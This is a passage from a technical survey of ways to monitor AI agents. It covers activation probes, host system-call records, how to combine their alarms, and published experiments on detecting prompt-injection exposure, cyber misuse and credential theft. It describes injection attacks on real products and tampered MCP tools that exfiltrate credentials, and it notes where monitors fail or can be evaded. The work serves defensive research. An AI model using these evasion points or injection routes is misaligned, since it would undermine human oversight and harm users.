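If V includes every possible function, this equals ordinary mutual information and the ceiling applies again. With a smaller V, processing X can increase the usable information. *A Bayesian Framework for Information-Theoretic Probing* (2021) reaches a similar result for an agent that has to learn from data. A language model does a lot of this processing when it reads a prompt, and a probe benefits from it with almost no extra computation.

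How much a probe adds must then be measured by experiment. In *Conditional probing*, Hewitt, Ethayarajh and colleagues (2021) train one classifier on a baseline and another on the baseline combined with the model's representations. The difference in performance shows what the representations add for that kind of classifier. For an agent, the baseline could be features of the text in the application record. Gao requires a similar comparison before crediting activations with any predictive value of their own, and in Gao's tests the activations met that requirement in two of four settings.

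The clearest advantage of probes is that they need little computation. In *Detecting High-Stakes Interactions with Activation Probes*, McKenzie, Pawar and colleagues (2025) trained probes to recognize conversations in which a model's answer could have serious consequences. The probes performed about as well as medium-sized language models that read the same text, with roughly a millionth of the computation. Adding just 32 labelled examples from the setting where the probes would run improved them significantly. But at a 1% false-positive rate, the best probe caught 43% of the high-stakes cases, against 55% for the best language model. This is roughly what one would expect from the ceiling, since a strong enough monitor that reads the text can outperform a simple probe that reads the activations.

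Probes are also fast. In Gao's test, capturing one layer added no measurable delay to a single request and a 0.067% delay when the model handled eight requests at once. *Prompt-Injection Probes Learn the Conversation, Not Just the Injection* (Kale and Vishwanath, 2026) reports that a detector built on a second language model takes on the order of a second per item, which could add minutes to a task if the detector runs before each of several hundred tool calls.

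Finally, the ceiling applies only if the observer has all of O, and observers outside the model provider often don't. Codex's log and Claude Code's default traces, for example, omit some of it. A probe score computed on the full text on the provider's server could therefore give the customer information that is missing from the customer's own log. Gao asks anyone who makes such a claim to state which text was missing.

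### What tools do outside the model's context

Unlike the activations, the host record is not determined by what the model read. Suppose two users install the same tool package, and an attacker has tampered with one copy. The tool descriptions, the tool call and the returned result are identical in both sessions, so the activations are too, and any probe gives both sessions the same score. The host records differ because the tampered copy also opens a credentials file and sends it off the machine.

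King and colleagues built attacks of this kind into real MCP packages. In one scenario, a package silently reads the credentials, writes them to a hidden temporary file and posts them to the attacker's server, while the user still gets the legitimate work they asked for. *When MCP Servers Attack* (2025) explains that this is easy because a malicious server can include arbitrary code that runs whenever the agent uses one of its resources. The model doesn't need to read the code for it to run.

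Adding the host record, H, to Gao's formula shows what a join could contribute. By the chain rule for mutual information,

I(Y; A, H | O) = I(Y; H | O) + I(Y; A | O, H)

The last term is zero because O still determines A, so an observer with the complete text, the host record and unlimited computing power would gain nothing from the activations. The theoretical case for adding the host record is strong, whereas the case for adding activations depends on cost, speed, ease of learning and missing text. These are good reasons, but an experiment has to show that they hold in a particular system.

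The host record also has gaps. An agent may upload a credentials file to the company's backup server because a user asked it to, or to an attacker's server because a hidden comment asked it to. The system calls can be identical except for the address. The second upload is theft because of who asked for it, and only the text shows that. King and colleagues also include an attack through retrieved references that affects only text and leaves no distinctive system calls.

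### Four combinations of alarms

Suppose an operator runs a probe on the model and a detection rule on the host, and joins their alarms by session. Each session then falls into one of four groups:

| | Host alarm | No host alarm |
|---|---|---|
| **Internal alarm** | The model acted on an injection or a harmful request, and the machine carried it out. Authorized security work can look the same. | The model read an injection but did not obey it, the harm happened on a remote service, or the probe reacted to harmless text. |
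| **No internal alarm** | A tampered tool or script acted without the model's knowledge, the probe missed an attack, or a harmless program behaved unusually. | The session was ordinary, or neither detector recognized the attack. |

When only the probe raises an alarm, the most likely explanation is often an injection that failed. Kale and Vishwanath tested six open models as agents, and the agents carried out the attacker's task in only 9–30% of runs, even with an injection format designed to look official. In *BASIS*, Qin, Zhu and colleagues (2026) asked the open model Qwen3-8B to judge the sentiment of texts and hid instructions in those texts. With one of their weaker prompt templates, 322 of 500 injected inputs did not change the model's behaviour. With the two strongest templates, none of the 500 changed it. A detector of injected text would still have flagged nearly all of these inputs.

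A monitor can partly separate exposure to an injection from commitment to obeying it by examining the model's internal states. Qin and colleagues measure how the model divides its attention between the developer's instructions and the outside data. (Attention weights differ from activations, but the idea also applies to activations.) They train one probe to detect an injection and another to predict whether the model will obey it, and reject an input only when both probes fire. With the template that left 322 inputs harmless, this reduced needless rejections from 100% to 12.4% of those inputs, but it let through successful attacks amounting to 1.6% of all injected inputs.

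The layer a probe reads may matter too. *Where Do LLMs Decide to Break the Rules?* (2026) found that a probe on the open model Qwen3-4B could detect early in the network whether an attack was present. Interventions before layer 19 almost never changed whether the model complied. An alarm from an early layer is therefore better evidence that the model has encountered an attack than that it will comply with it.

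Harm done on a remote system can also trigger an alarm from the model's internal states but not from the host record. Kale and Vishwanath list several attacks on real products in which this seems likely. In one, a message in a public GitHub issue led an agent to publish data from its user's private repositories in a public pull request. On the user's machine, that might appear as one more encrypted connection to a site that the agent contacts all day. In two others, a single crafted email made Microsoft 365 Copilot send internal data to an attacker, and a message in a public Slack channel made Slack AI leak private content through a link. Those assistants run on their vendors' servers, so the customer's host record would contain very little. If the probe also classified the request as routine, neither source would raise an alarm.

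A host alarm alone is harder to interpret because a tampered tool and an injection that the probe missed can produce the same host events. The application record helps distinguish them. If the tool call names the credentials file, the model generated the request for that file and the probe probably missed something. If the call only runs `setup.sh`, the script is more likely the cause.

Harmless activity will cause many host alarms. King and colleagues compared harmless and malicious sessions on the system-call features that best separate them. The two groups had the same median on each feature, and the differences were in the top tenth of values. Agents doing legitimate work start programs, search folders and contact outside servers, and most of an attack consists of the same actions.

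### Requiring both alarms or accepting either

Monitoring each session with two alarms requires a rule for combining them into one decision. Doctors face the same problem when a patient takes two tests. *A review of methods for the analysis of diagnostic tests performed in sequence* (Fanshawe, Nicholson and colleagues, 2024) describes the two simplest rules. The OR rule, or "believe the positive", makes a diagnosis if either test is positive, and the AND rule, or "believe the negative", requires both to be positive.

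In an invented example, ten of 10,000 sessions are harmful. A probe detects 90% of the harmful sessions and a host rule detects 80%, each with a false-positive rate of 5%. If their errors are independent, both flag a harmful session with probability 0.9 × 0.8 = 0.72 and a harmless one with probability 0.05 × 0.05 = 0.0025. An AND rule, which raises an alarm only when both detectors flag a session, therefore produces about 25 false alarms across the 9,990 harmless sessions.

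| Rule | Harmful sessions caught | False alarms | Share of alarms that are real |
|---|---|---|---|
| Probe alone | 9 | 500 | 1.8% |
| Host rule alone | 8 | 500 | 1.6% |
| Both, independent errors | 7.2 | 25 | 22% |
| Either, independent errors | 9.8 | 974 | 1.0% |
| Both, false alarms correlated at 0.3 | 7.2 | 167 | 4.1% |
| Either, false alarms correlated at 0.3 | 9.8 | 832 | 1.2% |

The last two rows drop the assumption that the false alarms are independent. If r is their correlation and f₁ and f₂ are the two false-positive rates, the rate at which both detectors flag a harmless session becomes

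f₁f₂ + r × √(f₁(1 − f₁) × f₂(1 − f₂))

With r = 0.3, the AND rule's false-alarm rate is 0.0025 + 0.3 × 0.0475 = 0.01675, or about 167 sessions. *Estimation of the sensitivity and specificity of two serum ELISAs*, a study of tests for an infection in sheep, uses the same correction, written in terms of covariances. A fairly modest correlation makes the AND rule's false alarms almost seven times as frequent. It slightly reduces the OR rule's false alarms, because those that coincide count only once.

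Correlation matters much less for the harmful sessions. The probe misses one of the ten and the host rule misses two, so however their misses overlap, the AND rule catches between seven and eight on average, and the OR rule between nine and ten. False alarms under the AND rule, however, could range from none to 500. An operator deciding whether the combination is worthwhile should therefore first measure how often both detectors flag the same harmless session, which can be done with ordinary traffic and no attacks.

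Even 22% may be too low for the people who answer the alarms. In *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000), Axelsson concluded from studies of operators in power stations, paper mills and similar plants that most people would lose faith in a detector by the time half of its alarms were false. With one harmful session in a thousand, staying within that limit again requires a false-positive rate of 0.1% or less.

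The AND rule would also miss nearly all attacks that involve tampered tools or remote actions, a weakness the averages don't show. A tampered tool gives the probe nothing to read, and a remote action may give the host rule nothing to flag. The probe's 90% in the example is plausible only if few of the ten harmful sessions involve tampered tools. An attacker who knows the AND rule is in use needs to evade only one detector, but would have to evade both under the OR rule.

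Operators can use more than one rule. For example, they could stop a session when both alarms fire and send single alarms to an automatic check that takes little compute. They could also run the tests in sequence, examining the host record closely only after the probe has fired. The danger, as Fanshawe and colleagues point out, is that if the first test misses a case, nobody performs the second, however good it is. For tampered tools, an operator who always started with the probe would almost never look at the host record, which contains the evidence.

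McKenzie and colleagues tried another combination, in which the probe scores every conversation and a language model also scores those the probe rates near the middle. Averaging the two scores for these uncertain cases worked better than either monitor alone with the same amount of compute. A score based on host activity could replace the language model's score, though nobody appears to have tested this.

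### Why false alarms may coincide

Some evidence suggests that probes make different mistakes from other monitors. McKenzie and colleagues found that adding a language model to a probe improved results even when the language model was the weaker monitor. *Activation Monitoring* found that the errors of its probes were uncorrelated with those of text classifiers. Both studies compared probes with monitors that read text. No published study seems to have measured the correlation between a probe's false alarms and a host rule's.

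*Aggregating multiple test results to improve medical decision-making* notes that researchers commonly assume tests are independent because this simplifies the mathematics, and gives a counterexample from COVID-19. Antibodies can take weeks to develop, by which time the infection may have cleared and a PCR test is likely to be negative. The antibody and PCR tests then disagree because they detect different stages of the same disease. A probe and a host rule could disagree about a real attack in the same way if the probe reacts when the agent reads the README and the host rule reacts when a scheduled script runs much later.

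In harmless sessions, the bigger worry is that the probe and the host rule will both raise false alarms. Suppose a company's security team asks an agent to test whether a stolen laptop would expose any credentials. The prompt discusses theft, the agent searches for secret files, and it may send a dummy file to a test server to see whether the firewall stops it. The text resembles the probe's harmful training examples and the system calls resemble an attack, so the same legitimate task triggers both alarms.

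Probes seem prone to this kind of mistake. Kale and Vishwanath cite an earlier deception probe that flagged conversations about deception even when the model answered honestly. In their own tests, they replaced injected instructions with harmless notices in the same format, and probes with standard training flagged 92–98% of the notices. Adding harmless look-alikes to the training data reduced this rate to 3–16% in applications the probes had been trained on, so the problem is at least partly fixable.

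A small amount of security work is enough to produce a correlation of 0.3 between two detectors' false alarms. Suppose 200 of the 9,990 harmless sessions are security work, and each detector independently flags 90% of them. Their flags then overlap on 162 of those sessions. To keep its overall false-positive rate at 5%, each detector must flag about 3.3% of the remaining sessions, where their flags overlap on only about ten. The total is 172 double false alarms, nearly all from the 2% of sessions that are security work, which corresponds to a correlation of 0.31.

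An operator could reduce these alarms by registering authorized security work in advance and judging it by different thresholds. The list of registered sessions would need protection, because an attacker who could add a session to it could easily evade both detectors. The registration should also come from outside the agent's context, since an attacker can inject a comment saying the work is part of a security test as easily as a real user can say so.

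### How false alarms accumulate over a session

The invented example counts one decision per session, but a monitor may check every tool call. If each check has a false-positive rate p and the checks are independent, the chance of at least one false alarm in n checks is

1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

If each check has a 5% false-positive rate, Gao calculates that the chance of at least one false positive is 22.6% for five checks, 40.1% for ten and 64.2% for twenty. The same formula gives 99.4% for a hundred checks, which a long coding session can easily reach. An operator can't interpret a false-positive rate without knowing whether it applies to a token, a tool call or a whole session.

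Checks within one session are rarely independent. A harmless README that sets off a probe stays in the context and may set it off again at every later request. Because these repeated alarms fall in the same session, fewer sessions have a false alarm than if the checks were independent. Gao shows that, however the checks depend on each other, the session's false-alarm rate lies between p, the rate for a single check, and n × p, where n is the number of checks. For ten checks at 5% each, the range is 5% to 50%.

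Keeping the false-positive rate at 5% per session requires a rate of about 0.5% per check for ten independent checks, and about 0.05% for a hundred. This requires a higher threshold, so the detector will miss more attacks.

Matching events to individual tool calls, and not just to sessions, can also reduce false alarms. Suppose a probe and a host rule each check ten tool calls per session, with 5% false alarms per call and independent errors. Each detector raises at least one false alarm in 40% of harmless sessions, and both do in 16%, or about 1,600 of the 9,990 harmless sessions. If the operator requires both alarms to belong to the same tool call, the chance of a false alarm falls to 0.25% per call and 2.5% over ten calls, or about 250 sessions.

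Requiring both detectors to raise an alarm on the same call removes fewer false alarms when both react to the same harmless activity, as with the security test, because their alarms then fall on the same call. This rule also misses attacks that spread over several steps, such as when the agent reads a comment at one call and obeys it at another. An operator could account for these attacks by following the links between steps and requiring the host event to trace back to the request that set off the probe.

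Low false-positive rates also take a lot of data to confirm. If a detector's true rate at some threshold is α, the chance that m independent harmless sessions all stay below the threshold is (1 − α)ᵐ. To be confident that the rate is no higher than α, with a risk δ of being wrong, Gao therefore requires at least

m ≥ ln δ / ln(1 − α)

This gives 59 sessions for a rate of 5% and a 5% risk of error, and 2,995 sessions for a rate of 0.1% at the same risk of error. A thousand tool calls from the same ten sessions aren't a thousand independent observations, because whatever is unusual about one session affects all of its calls.

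The same method works for a combined alarm, even if the two detectors are not independent. For the AND rule, the operator can put both scores on a common scale, take the lower one for each session, and set the threshold on that. The guarantee holds only while new sessions resemble the ones in the test. It can fail if the model or tools change, or if a security team starts using the agent for its own work.

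## Experiments that read the model's activations

Reflection AI, which develops the Beam language models, has run one of the largest published tests of a probe on a tool-using agent. *Monitoring Activations for Real-Time Detection of Cyber Misuse* (Alfano, Stein and colleagues, 2026) describes the company's Iris Cyber Probe. The probe reads Beam's activations at every token and scores whether a user is requesting help with a cyberattack or the model is providing it.

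### Iris Cyber Probe

A probe that averages over all tokens has a weakness in long sessions, because fifty harmful tokens barely move an average over 20,000. Iris carries a running summary of the conversation instead. It first shrinks each activation to a shorter vector. A small recurrent network, called a minGRU, then updates the summary h at each token t:

hₜ = (1 − gₜ) × hₜ₋₁ + gₜ × cₜ

Here cₜ is new content computed from the current token, and gₜ contains a number between 0 and 1 for each entry of the summary that sets how much of the old content to replace. The score is a weighted sum of the entries of hₜ, mapped to the range from 0 to 1. The amount of computation per token stays the same however long the session runs, and the probe has only about 350,000 parameters.

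Alfano and colleagues also labelled smaller pieces of text. Developers often train probes with one label for a whole turn or conversation, which doesn't show where the harm is. For Iris, a language model divided each conversation into chunks, each containing one request, action or explanation. A judge model then answered a fixed series of policy questions about each chunk, using the conversation up to that point. If its answers allowed more than one verdict, the chunk stayed unlabelled. A refusal that follows a harmful request counts as harmless, so the score should fall again when the model refuses. The training set had 52,387 conversations and more than a million labelled chunks, about 234,000 of them harmful.

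The probe was better at locating harm within a session when trained on chunk labels, but whole-session labels made it better at identifying which sessions contained harm. Linking activations to system calls requires accurate location, because an alarm has to flag the right tool call.

Iris detected 93.1% of the harmful chunks in 6,282 test conversations. Kimi K3, an open-weight language model that read the text of each chunk and what came before it, detected 72.7%. Both used thresholds that produced alarms on at most 5% of the harmless conversations in a separate validation set. Iris raised an alarm in 5.44% of the harmless test conversations.

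Reflection AI tested its own probe on its own model, using labels from its own judge. Iris was trained on a million of those labels, whereas Kimi K3 was given a written policy and one attempt per chunk. The 20-point gap therefore reflects training as well as access to activations. A text classifier trained on the same chunks would be a fairer comparison, but all three text monitors tested were general-purpose language models.

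Iris had no such lead on material unlike its training data. This test used 1,000 harmful and 750 harmless cybersecurity requests from the public benchmark CyberSecEval, each a single prompt. Iris caught 78.7% of the harmful requests and flagged 5.7% of the harmless ones, while Kimi K3 caught 75.5% and flagged 2.9%. At false-positive rates below 10%, all three text monitors were better than Iris at ranking harmful requests above harmless ones.

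False alarms were rarer in ordinary coding work. Iris flagged 0.56% of 3,217 harmless coding sessions, the longest of which had about a million tokens. The text monitors flagged less than 0.1%, but they judged each session as a whole rather than token by token. At a stricter setting, Iris flagged 0.09%, roughly the rate an operator would need if one session in a thousand were harmful, but it caught only 67.6% of the harmful CyberSecEval requests.

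Alfano and colleagues also replayed attacks that an automated attacker from the security company Gray Swan had already used successfully against Beam. The success rate falls from 8.27% to 0.56% if every attack that Iris flagged by the end of the response counts as blocked. At least one attack still succeeded for 16 of the 88 harmful behaviours tested. The attacker had never faced Iris, so these figures don't show how well Iris would block an attacker that had.

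For the speed test, Beam ran on four GPUs with 64 simultaneous users. When Iris shared one of those GPUs, output fell by 4.8% and the median wait for the first token rose from 288 to 385 milliseconds. Adding a fifth GPU just for Iris cut the loss to 0.6%, the figure in the paper's abstract, but required a quarter more GPUs. In both setups, users received each token only after its score had arrived, so a server could stop a harmful tool call before the agent software received all of it.

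One test session shows what such an alarm could add to a host record. The user describes a billing system that a company is retiring and asks the agent to overwrite its ledger with random bytes so that nobody can recover it. Iris flagged the request, the model's reasoning and the resulting `dd` command, and Kimi K3 flagged none of them. A host sensor would log a `dd` process writing to a database file, which is also what a legitimate decommissioning looks like. The probe's alarm would give an analyst a reason to check which it was. (A language model simulated the tools in this session, so it has no host record to compare.)

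### Detecting exposure

Iris looks for harm that the user requests. In an indirect prompt injection, the user's request is harmless. An alarm can then mean either that the model has only read the planted text or that it is about to obey it.

Exposure to prompt injections is fairly easy to detect. In *Your Agentic LLMs Secretly Encode Indirect Prompt-Injection Exposure in Hidden States*, Dong, Liu and colleagues (2026) ran eight open-weight models, from 2 billion to 2.8 trillion parameters, on AgentDojo. This benchmark plants injections in the emails, files and messages that a simulated agent reads. They labelled a point in a session positive if the latest tool result contained an injection, whatever the model did next. They applied a linear probe to the activation just before the model began its reply.

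Dong and colleagues trained the probes on eight combinations of attack wording, task set and agent instructions, and tested them on 16 combinations in which all three were new. AUROC ranged from 0.934 to 0.979. They picked each model's best layer using those same test results, which inflates these figures somewhat, although neighbouring layers usually carried the signal too.

The same models often obeyed the injections anyway. On difficult AgentDojo settings, attacks succeeded in 47.2% of runs on Qwen3-8B and 34.6% on Qwen3.5-27B. When Dong and colleagues used the probe's score to decide when to insert a short warning at the start of the model's reasoning, the rates fell to 2.9% and 0%, respectively. An exposure alarm is a good trigger for a small precaution, even though it gives little information about whether an attack would have worked.

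Dong and colleagues also fed transcripts from the other models' sessions to Qwen3-8B, and a probe on Qwen3-8B's activations detected exposure about as well as the probes on the models that had produced the sessions. A customer who cannot see a provider's activations could therefore run a small open model over its own application record and probe the small model's activations. This would show how the small model responds to the text, which is enough to detect exposure but presumably a weaker guide to what the provider's model will do.

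A probe can score highly on such tests for trivial reasons. In *When AUC 0.998 Is Not Enough*, Li, Fan and Zhuang (2026) tested Qwen2.5-VL-7B, a model that works from screenshots, on recorded web tasks. Their probe separated steps that showed a malicious banner from clean steps with an AUROC of 0.998. They then replaced the malicious text with gibberish of the same length, position, font and colour. The probe did not reliably score the malicious banner above the gibberish, so it may have detected little more than the presence of a banner. However, with only 20 test sessions, the experiment could have missed a moderate difference between the two.

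For injections in text, Li and colleagues could perfectly separate attacked steps from clean ones using four simple features, including how much longer the prompt was than its clean twin. Their probes scored only 0.705 and 0.771. Small training sets make such shortcuts more likely. When Dong and colleagues trained probes on few examples, the probes did much better on training data than in new settings, and the gap narrowed as they added examples.

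### Predicting commitment

In *Exposure Is Not Commitment*, Sinha (2026) asked whether a probe can predict that a model will obey an injection. The main test used Qwen2.5-7B on 280 office tasks from AgentDojo. The model read an injection and then called a harmful tool in 141 tasks, read an injection but did not call a harmful tool in 99, and encountered no injection in the other 40. The probes read activations from one layer at two points before the model wrote its tool call.

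Such a probe is usually trained to distinguish harmful cases from all others. The resulting probe separated attacked but safe cases from clean ones perfectly, with an AUROC of 1.000, but separated harmful from safe cases among those attacked with an AUROC of only 0.672. At a threshold of 0.5, it flagged all 141 harmful cases before the action, but also all 99 in which the model had resisted, so a flag did not show whether an attack would succeed.

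Sinha then trained probes only on the attacked cases. These all contain an injection, so detecting one doesn't help, and a probe has to use whatever distinguishes obeying the injection from resisting it. A logistic probe predicted the harmful call with an AUROC of 0.853. Part of the improvement comes from a better classifier, since the simpler probe from the first test, which compares an activation with the average harmful and average harmless ones, rose only from 0.672 to 0.763.

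The activations had no clear advantage over text for predicting obedience. A TF-IDF classifier, which weighs the words and word pairs in the visible context, reached 0.855. On entirely new tasks, the probe scored 0.795 and the text classifier 0.780. Activations did better than text on exposure, where the best trained text classifier reached 0.908. When Qwen rated the same contexts itself, it recognized injections almost perfectly but predicted its own obedience with an AUROC of only 0.615.

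Two more models gave similar results after retraining, but very different ones before it:

| Model | Trained on all cases: exposure | Trained on all cases: commitment | Trained on attacked cases: commitment (new tasks) | Text classifier, attacked cases (new tasks) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-7B | 1.000 | 0.672 | 0.853 (0.795) | 0.855 (0.780) |
| Mistral-7B | 0.282 | 0.835 | 0.896 (0.856) | 0.945 (0.806) |
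| OLMo-2-7B | 0.957 | 0.785 | 0.912 (0.905) | 0.921 (0.905) |

The Mistral probe's AUROC of 0.282 means that it usually ranked clean cases above attacked ones. In its training data, 313 of the 353 "safe" cases contained an injection that the model had resisted, so an injection was, if anything, associated with the "safe" label. A probe trained on mixed cases learns different things depending on the mixture, which a single overall AUROC does not show.

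These results bear on a dispute about whether probes can predict actions at all. Sinha recounts three negative results from *Internal-state probes read the situation, not the action* (Fomin, David and LeVi, 2026). One probe separated the paper's constructed examples perfectly but raised no alarm in any of 143 contexts after which the model acted unsafely, or in 342 further cases where part of the response was already filled in. The paper's best predictor of future behaviour had an AUROC of 0.801.

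Sinha argues that training on mixed cases can produce this pattern, but did not rerun their data. The two sides may be closer than their titles suggest, since an AUROC of 0.801 is about what Sinha's retrained Qwen probe achieved on new tasks, though the data differ. Much of the disagreement is then over whether a score near 0.8 counts as success, which depends on how an operator wants to use it.

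Four attack templates that the retrained probes had not seen were harder still. The logistic probe fell to 0.572, while the simpler probe held at 0.756 and the TF-IDF classifier at 0.794. Only 33 of the 160 cases in this test were harmful, so the ranking of the three could easily change.

A model's commitment to an unsafe response looks easier to predict in chat models without tools than in agents. In *Latent Safety Probes*, Li, Yang and colleagues (2026) trained a classifier on the activation at the end of the prompt to predict whether the response would be unsafe. On Llama-3.1-8B, its AUROC was 0.983 overall and 0.973 among harmful requests alone. For one request to depict violence, a probe for harmful requests gave a score of 0.998, but the classifier for unsafe responses gave 0.069, and the model refused. A chat model answers straight away, whereas an agent may read an injection and act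 on it several steps later, and this could explain some of the difference.

In the same study, the probes' apparent advantage depended heavily on the comparator. An earlier set of probes beat a crude refusal detector by 0.40 in AUROC but trailed the best safety-judging model by 0.01 at predicting behaviour. An attacker who targets a probe can also evade it, so detection rates measured on ordinary attacks are best cases.

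### When the model decides

If the model hasn't yet settled on an action, no monitor can reliably predict it. Jia, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *The Window Is in the Reasoning*, measured how much of the outcome is settled when the agent reads an injection. They replayed AgentDojo sessions exactly up to that point and then let the agent finish several times from each one. Let p be the share of reruns from a given starting point in which the agent obeys, and q the overall share. The part of the outcome settled at reading time is

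V = Var(p) / (q × (1 − q))

V is 1 if the starting point fully determines the result, and 0 if all starting points carry the same risk. Suppose half of the starting points lead to obedience 90% of the time and the other half 10% of the time. Then q is 0.5, the variance of p is 0.16, and V is 0.16 / 0.25 = 0.64.

V was 0.91 for Qwen3-8B answering without a reasoning step and 0.62 with reasoning switched on. Anything a monitor could read at that moment, whether text or activations, is the same in every rerun, so it can account for at most 62% of the variation in outcomes. The remaining variation depends on what the model writes next. On the banking tasks, V rose from 0.66 to 0.78 after 30% of the reasoning and to 0.87 after 70%.

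The three models in Sinha's tests do not reason before acting, so those AUROCs may be optimistic for agents that do. But the effect of reasoning varies by model. It reduced attacks on Qwen3-8B from 42% to 32% and raised them on Gemini 2.5 Flash from 62% to 80%. Even without reasoning, Gemini's outcomes were only about half settled at reading time.

Reading activations during the reasoning gave no early advantage. Jia and colleagues compared runs from the same starting point, so that differences in exposure could not help a monitor. In the first fifth of the reasoning, the probes' AUROC ranged from 0.07 below to 0.03 above that of TF-IDF. Later on, a probe scored 0.07 below the best achievable score on average, and Claude Opus 4.8 reading the reasoning scored 0.09 below it.

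Claude came within 0.02 when it judged simulated actions instead. The agent continued several times from its unfinished reasoning, and Claude checked the resulting tool calls for signs of a planted instruction. In one banking run, the reasoning was about last month's bill and didn't mention a password or the injection. The agent then changed the account password as the attacker wanted, and so did all four simulated continuations. Every monitor that read the reasoning gave a score near zero, while those that saw the calls rated an attack as nearly certain. The drawback is that each check needs several extra runs of the agent and, for longer attacks, a safe copy of its environment.

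Reruns also showed that, with reasoning on, two runs of the same case got different labels up to 35% of the time. A probe that correctly identifies a risky situation will therefore be marked wrong whenever the single recorded run happened to end well.

### Credential theft and harmful tool calls

Several groups have built probes for narrower targets. In *Caught in the Act(ivation)*, Chauhan and Revankar (2026) try to detect a request for credentials before the model writes anything. They take the activations at the end of the prompt from the last quarter of the model's layers and measure how far each one is from the average for harmless prompts, relative to the normal spread. A small neural network turns these distances into a score.

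On Qwen-7B, this reached an AUROC of 0.998 with 1.5% false positives, while four text monitors reached AUROCs of 0.73 to 0.90. The comparison is uneven because the text monitors read the model's output, where an encoded password may no longer look like a password. A text classifier that read the prompt might have done much better. Chauhan and Revankar describe their result as a controlled laboratory result, in which they knew where the credentials were.

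The study leaves out credentials that pass through the arguments of a tool call. In the running example, the model never needs to write the secret, because it only names the file and `curl` sends the contents. The host record captures this transfer, since the process has to open the file and connect to a server.

*Before Retrieval Begins* (Nawal, Baser and Gurusamy, 2026) supports the suspicion about text classifiers. The researchers gave seven open models of 3 to 12 billion parameters a web-retrieval tool and 296 harmful requests, each with a relevant web address. On six of the models, a probe that read the last input token separated harmful calls from neutral ones with an AUROC of 0.97 to 0.99. A classifier that used only short runs of characters in the request reached 0.97 to 0.98.

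The probe and the text classifier both had an easy task, because the neutral requests left out the harmful topic. When Nawal and colleagues tested harmless requests on the same topics, such as how to protect people from a dangerous substance, a probe trained without such requests wrongly flagged 91–100% of them. After they added such requests to the training data, the probe and the text classifier each caught over 98% of harmful calls at a 5% false-positive rate. A language model wrote the harmless requests to a template, so real ones may be harder to distinguish from harmful requests.

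The study also found that the model wrote a refusal alongside 33.6% of the harmful calls it made. Anyone reading only the reply would think the model had declined, but the call would appear in the application and host records.

### Unsafe sessions and tool errors

Some harm is visible only when an action is compared with what came before it. For example, an agent asked to review an invoice might pay the right supplier the right amount, and no single message would look harmful. In *Agent Safety from Within*, Jiao and Anderson (2026) built pairs of recorded sessions with identical messages and actions. The sessions in each pair differed only in that one had some information missing from the description of the tool the agent called. Three guard models, which are language models trained to label content safe or unsafe, did no better than chance at identifying the unsafe session in each pair.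 A simple direction in the same models' activations could be used to identify it with up to 94% accuracy.

The detector TACIT runs a finished session through a frozen open model and classifies the activations, so it works on transcripts from any agent, but only after the session has ended. Its performance was measured by macro-F1, which balances missed cases against false alarms and averages over safe and unsafe sessions. Across six benchmarks, a linear probe on Qwen3-4B scored 80.7, and a version that combined several layers scored 86.2. The best guard model scored 62.3.

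Most of the combined version's lead over the best guard depended on testing it on benchmarks it had trained on. When Jiao and Anderson left each benchmark out of training in turn, the combined version scored 65.7 and the best guard scored 61.1. On AgentDojo sessions, the combined version's score fell from 76.9 to 56.2. Operators whose agents and tools differ from those in the training benchmarks can expect scores closer to the lower figures.

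Probes can also look for mistakes that involve no attacker. In *The Calls are Coming from Inside the Model*, Yeats, Kennedy and colleagues (2026) tested 18 models on 750 function-calling exercises each. They used probes to predict whether a finished tool call was correct from the activation at its last token. Most probes scored above 0.80 AUROC, and they worked best in the middle and later layers. Perplexity, a measure of the model's uncertainty about its own words, averaged an AUROC of 0.62 for models of about 8 billion parameters and 0.80 for those with 70 billion. Many probes also kept an AUROC above 0.75 on types of error absent from their training. The errors covered include plausible but wrong arguments, such as the wrong folder in a delete command, which ordinary software checks would miss.

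Bhandari and Lingthep (2026), in *Do Benign-Trained Hidden-State Probes Detect Tool Errors Under Adversarial Conditions?*, got much weaker results on AgentDojo. They trained probes for three models on ordinary sessions and tested them on ordinary and attacked ones. In all 12 combinations of model and condition, the average uncertainty over the tool call's tokens detected tool errors better than the probe. The probe did worst on Qwen2.5-14B under an attack that overrides the system instructions, scoring 0.431, which is below chance, compared with 0.758 for the uncertainty measure. That was the only statistically significant difference after correction for the number of comparisons.

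Attacks can't be the whole explanation, because the probes also trailed on ordinary sessions. Bhandari and Lingthep read the final layer before the model had written the call, whereas Yeats and colleagues read several layers once the call was complete. Another difference is that AgentDojo tasks take many steps, while the function-calling exercises take one. For an operator who wants to catch mistaken calls, reading activations once the call is complete seems safer, and it still leaves time to block the call.

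### From scores to alarms

Nearly all of these results are AUROCs, which summarize performance across all thresholds, but an operator has to choose one. Gao ran the full procedure in four settings, two with chat prompts and two with agents. In each, Gao compared a monitor that reads text, one that reads activations, and one that combines them. Gao chose the thresholds from calibration data, not from the test results. Gao planned only the two agent tests in advance, having already seen earlier results on the chat benchmarks.

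To set the alarm threshold, Gao runs the monitor on harmless cases not used in training, sorts their scores, and picks one of the highest. A new case raises an alarm only if it scores above that threshold. If the calibration cases happen to have unusually low scores, the threshold will be too low.

Showing with 95% confidence that the false alarm rate is within a 5% budget takes at least 59 independent harmless cases, since 0.95⁵⁹ is just under 5%. A 10% budget takes at least 29. With so few cases, only the highest calibration score is a safe threshold. More cases allow a lower threshold, which misses fewer attacks. Gao could use the second-highest score with 100 cases and the twelfth-highest with 372.

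On AgentDojo, Gao ran Qwen2.5-7B ten times on each combination of task and injection. Such runs aren't independent, so Gao counted all ten as one case and represented it by the highest score among its harmless runs.

The AgentDojo monitors read the first request after the injection arrived and predicted whether the agent would carry out the attacker's goal. A secondary monitor, which averaged activations over the whole request, had an AUROC of 0.92 across individual runs. At the 5% alarm budget, however, it caught none of the 38 cases in which at least one run went wrong. The primary probe, which read only the last token, and the text monitor each caught two.

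A probe can have a high AUROC and still detect nothing. Suppose 90 of 100 harmless cases score low, the other ten score very high, and every harmful case falls in between. Each harmful case outranks 90% of the harmless ones, so the AUROC is 0.90. But any threshold that flags at most five harmless cases must be above every harmful case, so it detects none of them. Counting cases also lowers the AUROC, because each harmless case has ten chances to produce a high score. The primary AgentDojo probe had an AUROC of 0.80 when counted this way.

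With a 10% budget, the primary probe caught 20 of the 38 cases, but it also raised alarms in 14 of 75 cases with harmless runs (18.7%). An excess this large would have had a probability of about 0.2% if the calibration and test cases had come from the same population. The two sets of tasks evidently differed in some way that mattered, even though the benchmark and model were the same. An operator who adds a new tool or a new team of users could see a larger shift.

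The table gives results at the 5% budget. The AUROCs are for the combined monitor and count cases, not runs.

| Setting | Harmless calibration cases | AUROC, text and activations | Caught by text alone | Caught by text and activations |
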